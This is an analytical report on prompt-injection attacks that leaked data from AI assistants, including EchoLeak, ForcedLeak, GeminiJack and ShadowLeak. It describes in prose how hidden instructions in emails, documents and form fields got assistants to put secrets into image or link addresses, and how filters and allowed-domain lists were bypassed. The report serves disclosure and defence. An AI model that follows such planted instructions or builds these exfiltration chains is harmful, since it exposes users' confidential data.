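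Microsoft had closed the image leak in Bing Chat the year before, so Rehberger needed another way to get the data out. He chose a link and hid the email's text in it using invisible characters, because a web address that visibly contained a whole email would look suspicious.

Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to each text character, includes a set of "tag" characters that correspond to ordinary letters and digits but are invisible in most web applications. Rehberger credits Riley Goodside with discovering that language models can read them. It soon emerged that models can write them too. Rehberger calls this way of hiding text *ASCII smuggling*, after ASCII, an older code for basic English characters.

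The malicious email included a worked example that showed Copilot how to write in tag characters. Copilot used these characters to copy the other email's text into a link, then invited the user to click for details. Because the characters are invisible, the user saw a short, ordinary-looking address. A click sent the whole address to Rehberger's server, and he converted the hidden characters back into readable text. Hovering over such a link can reveal that something is odd about it, but the user can't read the secret there, whereas the developer in the Slack AI attack could. The trick also worked with links that open a new email, at least in some email programs.

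An attacker could also aim the instructions at one person. Copilot has access to the user's name, job title and manager, so an email can contain instructions that apply only when the chief executive's Copilot reads it. Other recipients could ask Copilot about the same email without triggering the attack.

Rehberger calls the combined attack reliable but gives no success rate. It still depended on a click, and he demonstrated it with emails he had prepared himself. In *Links and materials for Living off Microsoft Copilot*, Willison points to another Copilot data leak, which Michael Bargury presented at the DEF CON security conference in August 2024. In Bargury's video, the user only asks Copilot to summarise an email with hidden text.

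### Microsoft's six months

Rehberger first told Microsoft about the invisible characters on 17 January 2024. Microsoft closed the report a day later as low severity. He replied that combining the characters with other techniques would raise the severity, and got no response. On 10 February he sent a complete attack that extracted sales data, and three days later Microsoft opened an internal case. In March he added the version that stole Slack login codes.

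Rehberger had planned to present the attack at the HackSpaceCon conference in April, but he agreed to wait when Microsoft asked for time until the end of May. In mid-May Microsoft was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix. By 2 July the attack no longer worked when he tried it. He disclosed it in a talk on 24 August, after Microsoft had reviewed a draft of his post. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Exposes User Data Risks* dates the post to 26 August, six days after PromptArmor's report on Slack AI.

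Microsoft may have considered the invisible characters alone, which would help explain the first rating. An attacker can't use them to steal data without also having a way to inject instructions, a search that finds private data and a link that the user will click. But Copilot already had all three, and Rehberger combined them with the invisible characters in less than four weeks.

Rehberger had recommended that Copilot not display tag characters, not run searches automatically and, ideally, not display clickable links. He saw that links had disappeared from Copilot's answers but could not tell which other recommendations Microsoft had followed. When he asked for details so that other companies could learn from the fix, Microsoft did not answer. He added that Copilot was still open to prompt injection, which EchoLeak used in 2025.

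### Amazon Q stops displaying links

Amazon dealt with data leaks through links sooner. In Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business*, Rehberger describes testing the preview version of Amazon's new assistant for companies. He uploaded a text file with instructions, and Amazon Q produced what looked like a sign-in link, with a summary of the user's messages in its address. The demonstration extracted only chat history, but Rehberger warned that retrieval could also bring in hostile text.

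He reported the flaw on 4 December 2023, and Amazon deployed a fix worldwide on 29 December. After the fix, Amazon Q replaced each web address with a note saying it was not displaying the URL.

This fix is blunt, but it does not require Amazon to recognise an attack or decide which addresses are safe. OpenAI's `url_safe` service had to decide that for images, and Rehberger got data past it. The disadvantage is that employees often want a search assistant to link to the page behind an answer.

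The rule must also cover every link. In the Amazon Q post, Rehberger mentions that Microsoft 365 Chat was already replacing links with a privacy notice. Willison (2024) wrote about that post on 19 January in *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business*. About three weeks later, Rehberger sent Microsoft his attack, which used a link that worked in Copilot. He does not explain why this link was not replaced. Microsoft may have removed links from only some Copilot apps, or missed the kind of link he used.

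### Link previews remove the click

Slack builds link previews by automatically visiting the links in messages, which can leak data before anyone clicks. In *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do about it*, published on Embrace The Red, Rehberger describes the risk to a company that adds its own chatbot to Slack. If hidden instructions make the bot post a link with private data in its address, Slack sends the data to the attacker's server when it builds the preview. Willison (2024), in a post with the same title, wrote on 21 August that he had not thought about this leak before.

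Slack's own servers request the page for a link preview, so a content security policy cannot block the request. The attacker's log shows the visitor as Slack's link-expanding bot. PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI does not seem to have involved a preview, since the key was sent only when the developer clicked the link. The preview risk applies to other bots and assistants that post messages in Slack.

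A bot's developer can prevent the leak by turning off two preview settings when the bot posts a message. Slack shows previews by default, so each developer has to know about the problem. Anthropic missed the problem in a Slack connector it published as sample code for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting AI models to other programs.

In Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* (2025), a developer asks Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant, to analyse a file containing invisible instructions. Claude Code takes an API key from another file and posts it to Slack inside a link. When Slack previews the link, it sends the key to the attacker. In a second test, a user asks the Claude Desktop app to summarise a document for colleagues, and the app's post includes a link containing the latest message from another channel.

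The connector lets users restrict an assistant to a single private channel. Posting there seems harmless, and Rehberger expects many people to stop requiring the assistant to get approval for each message. But the restriction controls only where the message appears in Slack. The preview still sends the link's address to an outside server.

Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025, and Anthropic archived the connector two days later, though he does not know whether his report was the reason. Anthropic does not fix flaws in archived connectors, but people were still downloading this one more than 14,000 times a week. NIST's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025) describes the leak as zero-click and lists a CVSS score of 9.3 from the security firm VulnCheck. Rehberger scored the flaw 7.5.

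PromptArmor returned to link previews in early 2026, when people had begun using AI agents through messaging apps. For *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, it set up a website where users could test whether their app fetched links written by an agent. In its default configuration, OpenClaw, an agent that many people were trying at the time, leaked data through Telegram's link previews. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with agents from Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building custom assistants.

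PromptArmor's test could show that an app fetched such links, but not how often hidden instructions would cause an agent to write one. Participants also self-reported which agent they had used. PromptArmor wants messaging apps to let developers turn off previews for particular chats or channels. OpenClaw users on Telegram could already do so by adding one line to a configuration file.

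## January to June 2025: EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

EchoLeak was a chain of flaws in Microsoft 365 Copilot that let an outsider steal company data by sending an email. Aim Labs, the research team of the security start-up Aim Security, found it in January 2025, and Microsoft fixed it in May. Copilot was better defended than the chatbots of 2023. Microsoft screened incoming text for injected instructions, removed outside links and images from Copilot's answers, and limited which domains the page could load images from. EchoLeak got past all these defences, and the victim didn't have to click anything.

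The fullest account comes from the team itself, which later found ReLeak and is now part of Cato Networks. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the chain in order, including the attempts that only partly worked.

### One email and an ordinary question

Copilot is open only to a company's employees, so an outside attacker could not type anything into it and could only send an email. The attack on Slack AI had required an account in the victim's workspace, but EchoLeak required only the victim's email address. Ravia writes that the email could come from any sender.

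Copilot could read the employee's mailbox, OneDrive storage, Office files and Teams chats, as well as the company's internal SharePoint sites, where staff share documents. When the employee asked a question, Copilot put the matching passages into the model's input, along with the earlier conversation and details such as the user's and company's names. An attacker could use EchoLeak to steal anything in that input.

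That is a lot, but less than everything Copilot could search. In Rehberger's 2024 attack, the hidden instructions made Copilot run another search for sales figures or login codes. Ravia describes no such search in EchoLeak. The secret had to be in the input already, usually because the employee's current question or an earlier one in the same chat had brought it in.

The employee also had to use Copilot. Ravia describes Copilot retrieving the email in response to a user's question, and Reddy and Gujral also have the attack start with a question. The question did not have to be about the email or its sender, and it could come at any point in a chat. Some of the press coverage obscured the need for a question. Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, wrote that Copilot "scans the user’s emails in the background" and so reads the attacker's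 message, which, taken literally, would mean that the email could set off the attack as soon as it arrived.

### The injection classifier

Microsoft's first defence was the XPIA (cross-prompt injection attack) classifier, a filter meant to stop injected instructions before they reach the model. The classifier looked for text that seemed to be giving orders to an AI system. Aim Labs wrote its email as though the instructions were for the person receiving it, and never mentioned AI, assistants or Copilot. The classifier let the email through, and the model followed the instructions.

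The classifier did not determine whether a person or Copilot would act on the instructions. This is hard to judge from the text alone, because the same sentence can be harmless when a person reads it and harmful when Copilot does. Business email consists largely of requests to send a figure or fill in a form, so a filter that blocked every request would make Copilot useless for email. Ravia considers such a message inherently difficult, though not impossible, to detect. He also points to a shortage of training data, since an injection can be about any topic and in any tone or language.

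Rehberger had used a similar disguise against Google Bard in 2023, in a document claiming that the legal department required "everyone reading this document" to follow its steps (Embrace The Red). EchoLeak showed that this kind of wording could also defeat a classifier trained to catch injections.

### Links and images in a less common notation

Copilot's next defence removed links to outside websites from its answers. Rehberger had noticed links disappearing in 2024, after he reported his own attack. However, the filter recognised only the most common Markdown link format, where the address comes directly after the link's text.

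Markdown also has a reference style for links, which works like a footnote. A label follows the link's text, and a separate line gives the address for that label. Copilot's filter did not recognise this notation, but the program that displayed the answer did, and turned it into an ordinary clickable link. Aim Labs found several variants that got past the filter.

The filter checked how a link was written instead of where it led. If Microsoft had inspected the finished page, it would have found the same outside address whichever notation the model used. Willison (2025) credits Microsoft for allowing only links to approved internal pages, but writes that it forgot to apply the rule to the lesser-known format.

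This gave Aim Labs a working one-click attack. The email contained instructions for the model to add the most sensitive information in its input to the address of a link. If the employee clicked the link, the attacker's server would log the data, much as in the Slack AI attack.

The team then replaced the link with an image so that the user no longer had to click. Copilot's filter removed external images as well as links, but it missed both when they were written in reference style. When the model wrote an image this way, the browser tried to load it immediately.

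### The list of allowed domains

The browser blocked the image because the page's content security policy (CSP) did not allow the attacker's domain. The list of allowed sources that Ravia published has 29 different entries, 11 of which cover every subdomain of a domain. The list includes SharePoint, Teams, Bing and a LinkedIn image server. According to Embrace The Red, Microsoft's 2023 policy for Bing Chat allowed images from four domains.

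A CSP checks only which domain the browser contacts, so Aim Labs searched the allowed domains for a service that would pass the request on. A browser loading an image does not run code from the page it contacts, and Ravia adds that it would not follow a redirect, a reply sending it to another address. The allowed service would therefore have to contact the attacker's server itself.

SharePoint was the obvious candidate, since an attacker can set up their own SharePoint site on an allowed domain. Two simple methods failed because Microsoft no longer lets developers run their own server code in SharePoint pages or pass data from a page's address to Power Automate, its automation service. The team then found a SharePoint function that fetches content from another website so that a page can embed it. If the image address pointed to this function and contained the attacker's address and the secret,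 SharePoint's server would send the secret to the attacker.

The SharePoint route completed the chain, but the victim had to be signed in to SharePoint and accept an invitation to the attacker's site. An employee who had never heard of the site would have little reason to accept.

Aim Labs then found an address on a Teams domain that served the same purpose without requiring an invitation. Reddy and Gujral describe it as part of the system Teams uses for previews. In the finished attack, Copilot's reply includes an image whose address points to Teams and contains the attacker's address with the secret attached. The browser sends the request because the Teams domain is allowed. Teams then contacts the attacker's server and sends it the secret.

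Willison describes the Teams address as an open redirect, a page that forwards visitors to any address they specify. Ravia's account fits a relay better, because he says the Teams address has the same outcome as the SharePoint function, whose server makes the request itself. With a redirect, the browser would have had to contact the attacker's domain, which the CSP did not allow. With a relay, a company checking its own network records would find only a request to Teams, and the attacker's log would show a visit from Microsoft. Reddy and Gujral leave open whether the log would show Microsoft's server or the victim's network address.

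Google's policy for Bard had the same weakness in 2023, when it allowed a domain where Google runs programs written by the public. The EchoLeak attacker did not need to write a program, because Microsoft's service fetched the address on request.

Adir Gruss, Aim Security's co-founder and chief technology officer, told Goldman that Microsoft had tried to block the attack at several points and failed "because AI is so unpredictable and the attack surface is so big". Unpredictability may explain why the classifier missed the email, but it does not explain why the link filter missed reference-style links every time or why the Teams address relayed whatever it was given. An ordinary review of the web software could have found both of these problems without involving a language model.

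### Keeping the email out of the answer

Copilot's answers refer to the material they draw on, which might have led the employee to the strange email. Aim Labs prevented this by including an instruction in the email that its "recipient" should never refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out. Reddy and Gujral write that the victim would have noticed at most what looked like a broken link or image.

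In the Slack AI demonstration, the attacker's message was also missing from the citations, but PromptArmor considered this a malfunction. With EchoLeak, an attacker could cause the omission deliberately. If text in the model's input can influence which sources the model cites, the list of sources is least reliable when someone has tampered with the input.

### RAG spraying

The attack works only if Copilot retrieves the email. The attacker could research the company and guess what its staff will ask, but Ravia writes that this gives a fairly poor retrieval rate. Aim Labs developed a technique it calls *RAG spraying*, where RAG is retrieval-augmented generation, or adding retrieved text to a model's input.

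Ravia explains the technique using a common kind of search system, but cautions that Copilot may work differently. An embedding model converts each piece of text into a long list of numbers, which acts like a position on a map, with texts of similar meaning close together. The system converts the user's question in the same way and retrieves the texts nearest to it. An email with one position is near only a few possible questions. To reach more of them, the attacker can send many emails, or one long email that the system splits into chunks, each with its own position.

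Aim Labs chose the long email. Its first idea was to repeat the instructions with random changes, such as extra characters or a 5 in place of an s. The model would still interpret the altered text correctly, but the embedding model might place it elsewhere on the map. The team tested this on OpenAI's `text-embedding-ada-002` embedding model, measuring similarity on a scale where identical texts score 1. An altered copy could score as low as 0.7 against the original. Two unrelated phrases, one about greeting cards and one about the philosophy of science, scored higher.

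The test supported the idea, but the team could not use it against Copilot. Working out which changes would spread the copies evenly requires knowing which embedding model Copilot uses, and Microsoft has not published that. The team instead used the simpler email described earlier, in which each passage claims to be a complete guide to a common staff question. Copilot retrieved this email in response to questions on various topics, but Ravia does not report how often.

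Matching an attacker's text to the victim's likely topic was already a known technique. In 2024 the security firm HiddenLayer told SC Media that an attacker who knew someone was planning a trip could name a document "Travel itinerary" to make Google's Gemini more likely to use it. In the Slack AI demonstration, the attacker mentioned the service whose key they wanted. With RAG spraying, the attacker no longer has to know what the victim is working on.

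The topics that are easiest to predict may not yield the most valuable data, however, because EchoLeak could take only what was already in the model's input. A question about parental leave will mostly bring up leave policies. The attacker would do better if the employee asked it in a chat that had earlier dealt with a merger, or if some of the guides covered topics closer to the company's secrets. Ravia does not discuss this trade-off.

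### What "LLM scope violation" means

Aim Labs also introduced the term *LLM scope violation*. Ravia uses it for attacks in which instructions from an untrusted source make a model use trusted data in its input without the user's explicit consent. In EchoLeak, an email from outside the company contained a sentence instructing the model to look for secrets in the rest of its input. Ravia calls this sentence the "core red flag" because it refers to information beyond the email.

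He compares the model to a Unix *suid* program, which runs with its owner's permissions even when a user with fewer permissions starts it. That user can exploit a carelessly written one to open files they could not open directly. Similarly, the outsider who sends the email cannot read internal documents, but the model can, and it follows the instructions in the email.

Ravia accepts that EchoLeak is best classified as indirect prompt injection, but wants a more specific category so that developers can build more specific defences. His example is the stack overflow, a type of memory error within the broader category of buffer overflows. Once programmers had singled out stack overflows, they could protect against them with a *stack canary*, a known value placed in memory next to the data an attacker wants to overwrite. If the value has changed, the program stops.

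Willison thinks EchoLeak shows no new pattern and the term is unnecessary, because every prompt injection exploits the model's inability to take into account where text came from.

The older cases support him. The Google Doc that Rehberger used against Bard contained a request for the first 20 words of the conversation, and the message in the Slack AI attack contained a request for a key from a private channel. Both attacks used untrusted text to direct a model to data elsewhere in its input. They were LLM scope violations before anyone used the phrase, so it doesn't name a new kind of attack.

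It may be more useful as a suggestion about what a filter should look for. The XPIA classifier had to decide whether an email contained instructions for an AI, which an attacker could easily disguise. A filter that checks whether an outsider's email directs the model to other people's data could catch some malicious emails that are phrased politely to a human reader. It would also catch some honest ones. If a customer asks for the latest price list and an employee has Copilot draft the reply, Copilot must use internal data to answer an outside request.

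The comparison with stack canaries is also weaker than it looks, because a program can check whether a value in memory has changed without interpreting it, while deciding what a sentence in an email refers to requires understanding the sentence. The defender must therefore again rely on a classifier that an attacker can try to fool. Aim Security also had a commercial interest, since it was selling a guardrail against LLM scope violations when it introduced the term.

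Goldman's article gives a different definition, in which the model reaches data it isn't authorised to handle. That definition misses why EchoLeak was hard to stop. Copilot had permission to read every document involved because the employee did, and the permission system worked correctly throughout the attack.

### From the January report to the June advisory

Gruss told Goldman that the team spent about three months working out how Copilot operates. The team found the flaw in January 2025 and reported it to the Microsoft Security Response Center. Gruss said Microsoft called the findings "super groundbreaking".

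Microsoft attempted a fix in April. Lutra Security's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) shows that the flaw's identifier was reserved on 9 April. In May, according to Gruss, Microsoft found further security issues around the flaw. Aim Security withheld its research until the fix was complete, and hoped that publishing it would alert other companies with similar products.

Reddy and Gujral date the final fix to May. Microsoft applied the fix on its own servers and published its advisory on 11 June, the same day as Aim Security's findings and Goldman's article. The advisory, copied in exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), says that Microsoft had fully mitigated the flaw, that users did not need to do anything, and that Microsoft was publishing the CVE only for transparency. Microsoft gave the flaw a CVSS score of 9.3.

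Positive Technologies' *PT-2025-25212* (2025), an entry in a vulnerability database, tells customers to use a version of Copilot released in May 2025 or later. The advice makes little sense for a service that Microsoft runs and updates itself. The same entry says EchoLeak used ASCII smuggling, the invisible-character trick from Rehberger's 2024 attack, but Ravia's account does not mention the technique.

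Gruss considered five months "on the (very) high side" for such a fix. He attributed part of the delay to the novelty of the flaw, because it took time to find the right teams at Microsoft and explain the problem to them. That explanation is only partly convincing, because Microsoft should already have had people who knew the problem. It had fixed an image leak in Bing Chat two years earlier, and in 2024 it had spent about five months on Rehberger's complete attack against Copilot. The failed attempt in April suggests that the number of variants also slowed the fix. Aim Labs had reported several versions of the chain, involving different Microsoft products, and Microsoft would have had to deal with all of them.

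Microsoft has not explained what it changed. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content. They also mention "reported" options to stop Copilot from using outside messages in certain contexts, but do not say who reported them. They had no access to Copilot's internals. It is therefore unclear whether Microsoft closed the Teams relay, repaired the link filter or did both.

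A Microsoft spokesperson told Goldman that Aim had reported the issue in time for Microsoft to address it "before our customers were impacted". The advisory also lists the flaw as not exploited, and Aim Labs knew of no affected customers. Microsoft did not say how it had checked. It was best placed to do so because any stolen data would have passed through its Teams servers, but it did not mention searching their logs in either the statement or the advisory.

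### Could a company have protected itself?

Aim's advice to customers changed between two versions of its findings. On its original EchoLeak page, Aim Security wrote that Copilot's default configuration put companies at risk, and that they could use data loss prevention (DLP) tags or configure Copilot to ignore outside emails. DLP tools apply a company's rules for handling sensitive material. In the version on Cato's website, Ravia wrote that, to the team's knowledge, no administrator setting could have prevented the attack.

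Microsoft's announcements fit the second version better. On 5 June 2025, after the fix, Microsoft (2025) said administrators would soon be able to stop Copilot from processing emails with sensitivity labels, the markings a company puts on confidential material. The preview was due that month and applied only to emails sent since the start of the year. The setting could have protected a labelled internal email from EchoLeak, but it would not have stopped an attacker's unlabelled message from reaching the model.

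In May 2026, Microsoft's *DLP to restrict processing external emails in M365 Copilot and Copilot Chat* (2026) announced a control to restrict Copilot's processing of outside emails, with a preview in June 2026 and general release planned for June 2027. Companies may have had a cruder way to do this in early 2025, but the announcement presents the control as new. An employee could have avoided the attack only by not using Copilot, because the question that triggered it was not careless.

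### Whether EchoLeak was the first zero-click attack

Goldman's article called EchoLeak the first known zero-click attack on an AI agent. Ravia makes several versions of the claim, the broadest being that it is the first known zero-click AI vulnerability. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* repeated this as the first "ever discovered". The narrowest version covers only attacks on widely used generative AI products, and only those that work without specific user behaviour and without limits on what data can be taken. Ravia says that in earlier attacks, either the user explicitly pointed the chatbot to a malicious source or the attacker could take only very limited data.

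The Bing Chat attack had sent out data without a click in April 2023, 21 months before Aim Labs found EchoLeak, so the broad claim is wrong. Rehberger had also used the words "zero click" in his post on Bard to describe an image loading automatically.

The narrow claim is more defensible, as a comparison with the main earlier cases shows.

| Attack | How the instructions reached the assistant | Click needed? | What leaked |
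|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, March 2023 | The user pasted text copied from the attacker's website | No | Text from the chat |
| Bing Chat, April 2023 | The user opened a web page and chatted about it | No | A summary of the page and chat, and a secret on the page |
| Google Bard, September 2023 | The user had Bard read a Google Doc | No | The first 20 words of the chat |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, early 2024 | The user asked about an email or shared document | Yes | Text from other emails |
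| Slack AI, August 2024 | Retrieval found a message in a public channel | Yes | An API key from a private channel |
| EchoLeak, January 2025 | Retrieval found an email from outside | No | Anything in the model's input |

Slack AI had retrieved an attacker's message that the victim did not know about, and the chatbots of 2023 had sent out data without a click. EchoLeak did both at once in a product connected to a company's mail and files, which none of the earlier attacks in the table had done. Rehberger had warned of such an attack in his 2023 post on Bard but had not demonstrated it.

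Even the narrow claim slightly understates the Bing Chat attack. The user had to open the page, but it could be a legitimate page where the attacker had only posted a comment. That user would have had no more reason to be suspicious than an employee who asks Copilot about leave.

The word "agent" also overstates Copilot's role. Goldman defines an agent as an AI that acts autonomously to achieve specific goals, whereas Copilot in this attack searched for material and wrote an answer. Reddy and Gujral point out that it could not send an email on its own. The browser and the Teams server sent the data out by fetching an image, as they would any other image.

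### The case study by Reddy and Gujral

Aim Labs discovered EchoLeak, but some web pages credit it to Pavan Reddy and Aditya Sanjay Gujral of George Washington University. Reddy and Gujral wrote a case study about two months after the disclosure and published it in a symposium series of the Association for the Advancement of Artificial Intelligence. Their paper clearly credits Aim Labs with the discovery. The confusion probably comes from its title, which calls EchoLeak the first real-world exploit of its kind and can look like the announcement of a discovery.

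The study is useful for its explicit account of what the attacker and victim must do, and it proposes a range of defences. It contains no new evidence about the attack, because Reddy and Gujral worked only from public information and state that they did not reproduce EchoLeak or run any experiments. This makes the paper's grid of defences and attack steps misleading. The grid is labelled "theoretical", but the accompanying text says that its tick marks show full coverage "in our tests". Since there were no tests, the tick marks can only be the researchers' expectations. The paper also says that Microsoft issued "emergency patches", although its timeline runs from a report in January to a fix in May.

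Reddy and Gujral's most questionable claim is that before EchoLeak, prompt injection attacks had been "largely considered theoretical", with no confirmed real-world breaches. But since 2023, companies had been fixing flaws exposed by demonstrated attacks, as the cases of Bing Chat and Bard show. Embrace The Red also reports that Microsoft fixed the same image leak in Azure AI Playground, a site for trying out models, and that Anthropic had fixed it in Claude. In June 2024, Willison (2024) called the flaw in GitHub's Copilot Chat "yet another example of the same vulnerability" and listed five earlier products.

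There may have been no confirmed breaches before EchoLeak, but that does not set it apart, because Microsoft says that no customer lost data to EchoLeak either. Like the Bing Chat leak two years earlier, it was a demonstration by researchers against a working product.

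## From mid-2025: leaks through trusted domains and providers' own servers

After Microsoft fixed EchoLeak, researchers kept finding similar leaks. Between August 2025 and January 2026 they published attacks on ChatGPT, Salesforce's Agentforce, Google's Gemini Enterprise and, again, Microsoft 365 Copilot. In most of these attacks the data left through the user's browser, as it had in EchoLeak. A vendor can limit which addresses the browser contacts, and a company can look for the browser's requests in its network records. But in two attacks on ChatGPT, OpenAI's servers contacted the attacker directly, so neither measure helped.

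### Trusted domains that outsiders could use

By the summer of 2025, the Connectors feature let ChatGPT search a user's Google Drive, SharePoint, GitHub and other services. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes an attack in which the user uploads a document from an outsider and asks for a summary. Instructions in tiny white type in the document tell ChatGPT to search the user's Google Drive for API keys and put them into the address of an image. Zenity Labs added a story about a developer with a deadline to the instructions because ChatGPT tends to refuse to handle such keys.

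OpenAI's `url_safe` service, which had checked image addresses since December 2023, first rejected the researchers' server. They switched to Azure Blob Storage, Microsoft's file-hosting service, and ChatGPT displayed the image. Azure can log every request for a stored file, including any data added to the address, so an attacker can collect the data by storing an image there and reading the log. Writer had made the same mistake in 2023 by trusting Amazon's CloudFront.

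The user doesn't have to click anything after the upload. The OECD's *ChatGPT Connectors Vulnerability Enables Zero-Click Data Theft via Poisoned Documents* (2025) includes an AI-generated summary that describes the attack as requiring no user interaction, which overlooks the upload. In EchoLeak, by contrast, the victim never had to interact with the attacker's message. Zenity Labs points out that a malicious insider could plant instructions in many company documents and wait for colleagues to upload one. Its report doesn't mention a fix for the Azure route. Zenity Labs also uses the name AgentFlayer for a whole family of attacks, including some on Microsoft Copilot, so news about "AgentFlayer" may concern a different attack.

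In November 2025, Willison reported PromptArmor's finding that the browser tool in Google's Antigravity could by default visit only approved domains, but that these included webhook.site, a service for recording web requests where anyone can create an address and see what is sent to it. In PromptArmor's attack, hidden text on a web page posing as a technical guide made Antigravity collect the user's Amazon cloud credentials and send them to such an address. Antigravity's default settings stopped the model from opening the credentials file directly, so the model read it with a system command.

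Salesforce's list failed because it was out of date. Agentforce, the company's AI agent product, works with a business's customer records. Some of these records come from Web-to-Lead, a form on the business's website where potential customers (leads) enter their details. An attacker can type instructions into the form, and Agentforce reads them when an employee asks about that lead. The attacker doesn't need an account or an employee's email address.

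Sasi Levi and the security firm Noma found this flaw and named it ForcedLeak. Willison's *ForcedLeak* shows that the injected text was a short list of questions, including a harmless one about mixing colours. The text also asked for the leads' email addresses and for an image whose URL contained the answer. Salesforce's CSP blocked images from unknown domains but allowed my-salesforce-cms.com, whose registration had expired. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, the domain was for sale for $5. Noma registered it and received the lead data in its server's log, without the employee clicking anything. Hackread also lists sales plans, internal communications and historical records among the data at risk.

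Noma said that exfiltration "would have been impossible" without a way past the CSP, according to Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users. Salesforce's policy would have stopped ForcedLeak if it had not still included one expired domain. In the attacks on Bard and Microsoft 365 Copilot, by contrast, outsiders could receive data through domains that the vendor did control.

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later, according to the timeline in Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*. Salesforce took back the domain and corrected the CSP. On 8 September it also began enforcing a list of trusted URLs for its AI agents, and Noma published its findings on 25 September. According to The Hacker News (2025), the new list limits where the agents can send their output. This adds a check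 before the browser is involved, but it is another list of trusted domains, so Salesforce has to keep checking that each one still belongs to its original owner.

### Images and diagrams that got past the filters

The leaks in Gemini Enterprise and Microsoft 365 Copilot also went through the browser, but they seem to have reached the attacker's server without a trusted domain.

In June 2025, Noma found the leak in Gemini Enterprise, Google's set of AI assistants for companies, and called it GeminiJack. Expert Insights' *GeminiJack Flaw Shows How A Single Poisoned Workspace File Could Hijack Enterprise* (2025) explains that the attacker hides instructions in a Google Doc, a calendar invitation or an email. When an employee later runs an ordinary search, Gemini retrieves the attacker's text along with the material the employee wants. The instructions make Gemini search for private data in sources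 including email, calendars and documents, and put it into the address of an image.

GeminiJack resembles EchoLeak more closely than AgentFlayer does, because the employee does not have to open the attacker's file, upload it or click a link. But getting the data out was easier than in EchoLeak. In TechNadu's *New AI-Native Threat*, Levi attributes the leak to unfiltered HTML, which let an image tag contact the attacker's server. Google had fixed the same weakness in AI Studio in August 2024, but apparently not in Gemini Enterprise.

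According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data*, Noma reported the flaw the day it was discovered. SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* says Google had resolved it by November 2025 but gave no technical details. Expert Insights reports that Google separated Gemini Enterprise from Vertex AI Search, a related service for building search tools, which had the same flaw. Ticong (2025), in *GeminiJack Zero-Click Flaw Exposed Millions of Users in Google Workspace AI*, adds that Google changed how the system handles retrieved content. These changes address how the attacker's text gets in, whereas Google's earlier repairs mostly addressed how data gets out. Ticong also writes that "millions of users were affected", which presumably refers to people whose data an attack could have reached, not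 people who lost data.

The new leak in Microsoft's Copilot involved Mermaid, a text notation for diagrams that Copilot can display. Security researcher Adam Logue hid white text across several sheets of an Excel file. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, the attack starts when a user asks Copilot to summarise the file. The hidden text makes Copilot fetch the user's recent emails instead. Copilot then encodes them in hexadecimal and draws a diagram that looks like a login button, whose link contains the encoded emails.

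The attacker receives the emails only if the user clicks that button, according to a summary of Logue's post on daily.dev. The click is the last step, as it was in Rehberger's 2024 attack on the same product. Cyber Security News writes that the newer attack needs no direct interaction "beyond an initial click", which could wrongly suggest that the click starts it. Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) contrasts the flaw with an earlier one in Cursor, a programming tool, where a Mermaid diagram could leak data without any click.

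EchoLeak had bypassed Copilot's link filter with a less common Markdown notation, and Logue bypassed it by putting the link in a diagram. A CSP would not have helped, because it does not restrict which links a person opens. A filter of this kind needs a separate check for each new format that the assistant can display.

Logue reported the flaw on 15 August 2025. Microsoft confirmed it on 8 September and fixed it on 26 September, six weeks after the report. EchoLeak took about five months to fix. Microsoft simply stopped users from interacting with the contents of diagrams, including links, which few people will miss. Logue received no reward because Microsoft 365 Copilot was outside the scope of the company's reward programme at the time.

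### Requests from OpenAI's own servers

ChatGPT's Deep Research mode can send data out without using the user's browser. The mode, which OpenAI launched in February 2025, spends five to thirty minutes reading websites and documents and then writes a report. It can also read the user's Gmail if the user connects it. Deep Research opens web pages from OpenAI's servers, so if hidden instructions make it open an attacker's page, that request also comes from OpenAI's servers.

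*ShadowLeak*, by the security company Radware, demonstrates such an attack with two emails. One is a genuine message containing an employee's name and home address. The other is from the attacker and looks like a follow-up about a company restructuring, but it contains instructions that the reader may not be able to see. The user asks ChatGPT's Deep Research to search the day's emails for information about the process for a new employee. Deep Research reads both messages, adds the name and home address to a URL on the attacker's server, and opens that URL. Nothing unusual appears on the user's screen, and ChatGPT does not ask for confirmation.

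Large companies often route their employees' web traffic through a gateway that records and blocks suspicious destinations, and they install monitoring software on laptops. Neither detects this leak, because the laptop exchanges data only with ChatGPT, as the company expects, while the stolen data travels from OpenAI's servers to the attacker's without crossing the company's network. EchoLeak's Teams relay and a later Bing relay that the Cloud Security Alliance describes both began with a request from the employee's browser. But after ShadowLeak, only OpenAI and the attacker would have a record of the contact, so the company would depend on OpenAI to find out what happened.

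Radware sells software for monitoring AI agents, so it benefits when customers worry about this blind spot. In Radware's press release for a later attack, Pascal Geenens, its vice president for threat intelligence, says that companies "lack visibility" into what agents do in the cloud. For ShadowLeak, at least, this is true regardless of Radware's interest, because the request starts on the provider's own servers.

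The attacker could also send data to their own server, which gave them more choice of destination than in the browser attacks. Zenity Labs had to find a service that `url_safe` accepted, but Radware observed no comparable restriction on the pages that Deep Research could open. Radware demonstrated the attack only with Gmail but expects it to work with other services that Deep Research can read, such as Google Drive, Outlook, Teams and GitHub. That seems likely, since text from any of them can reach the model in the same way.

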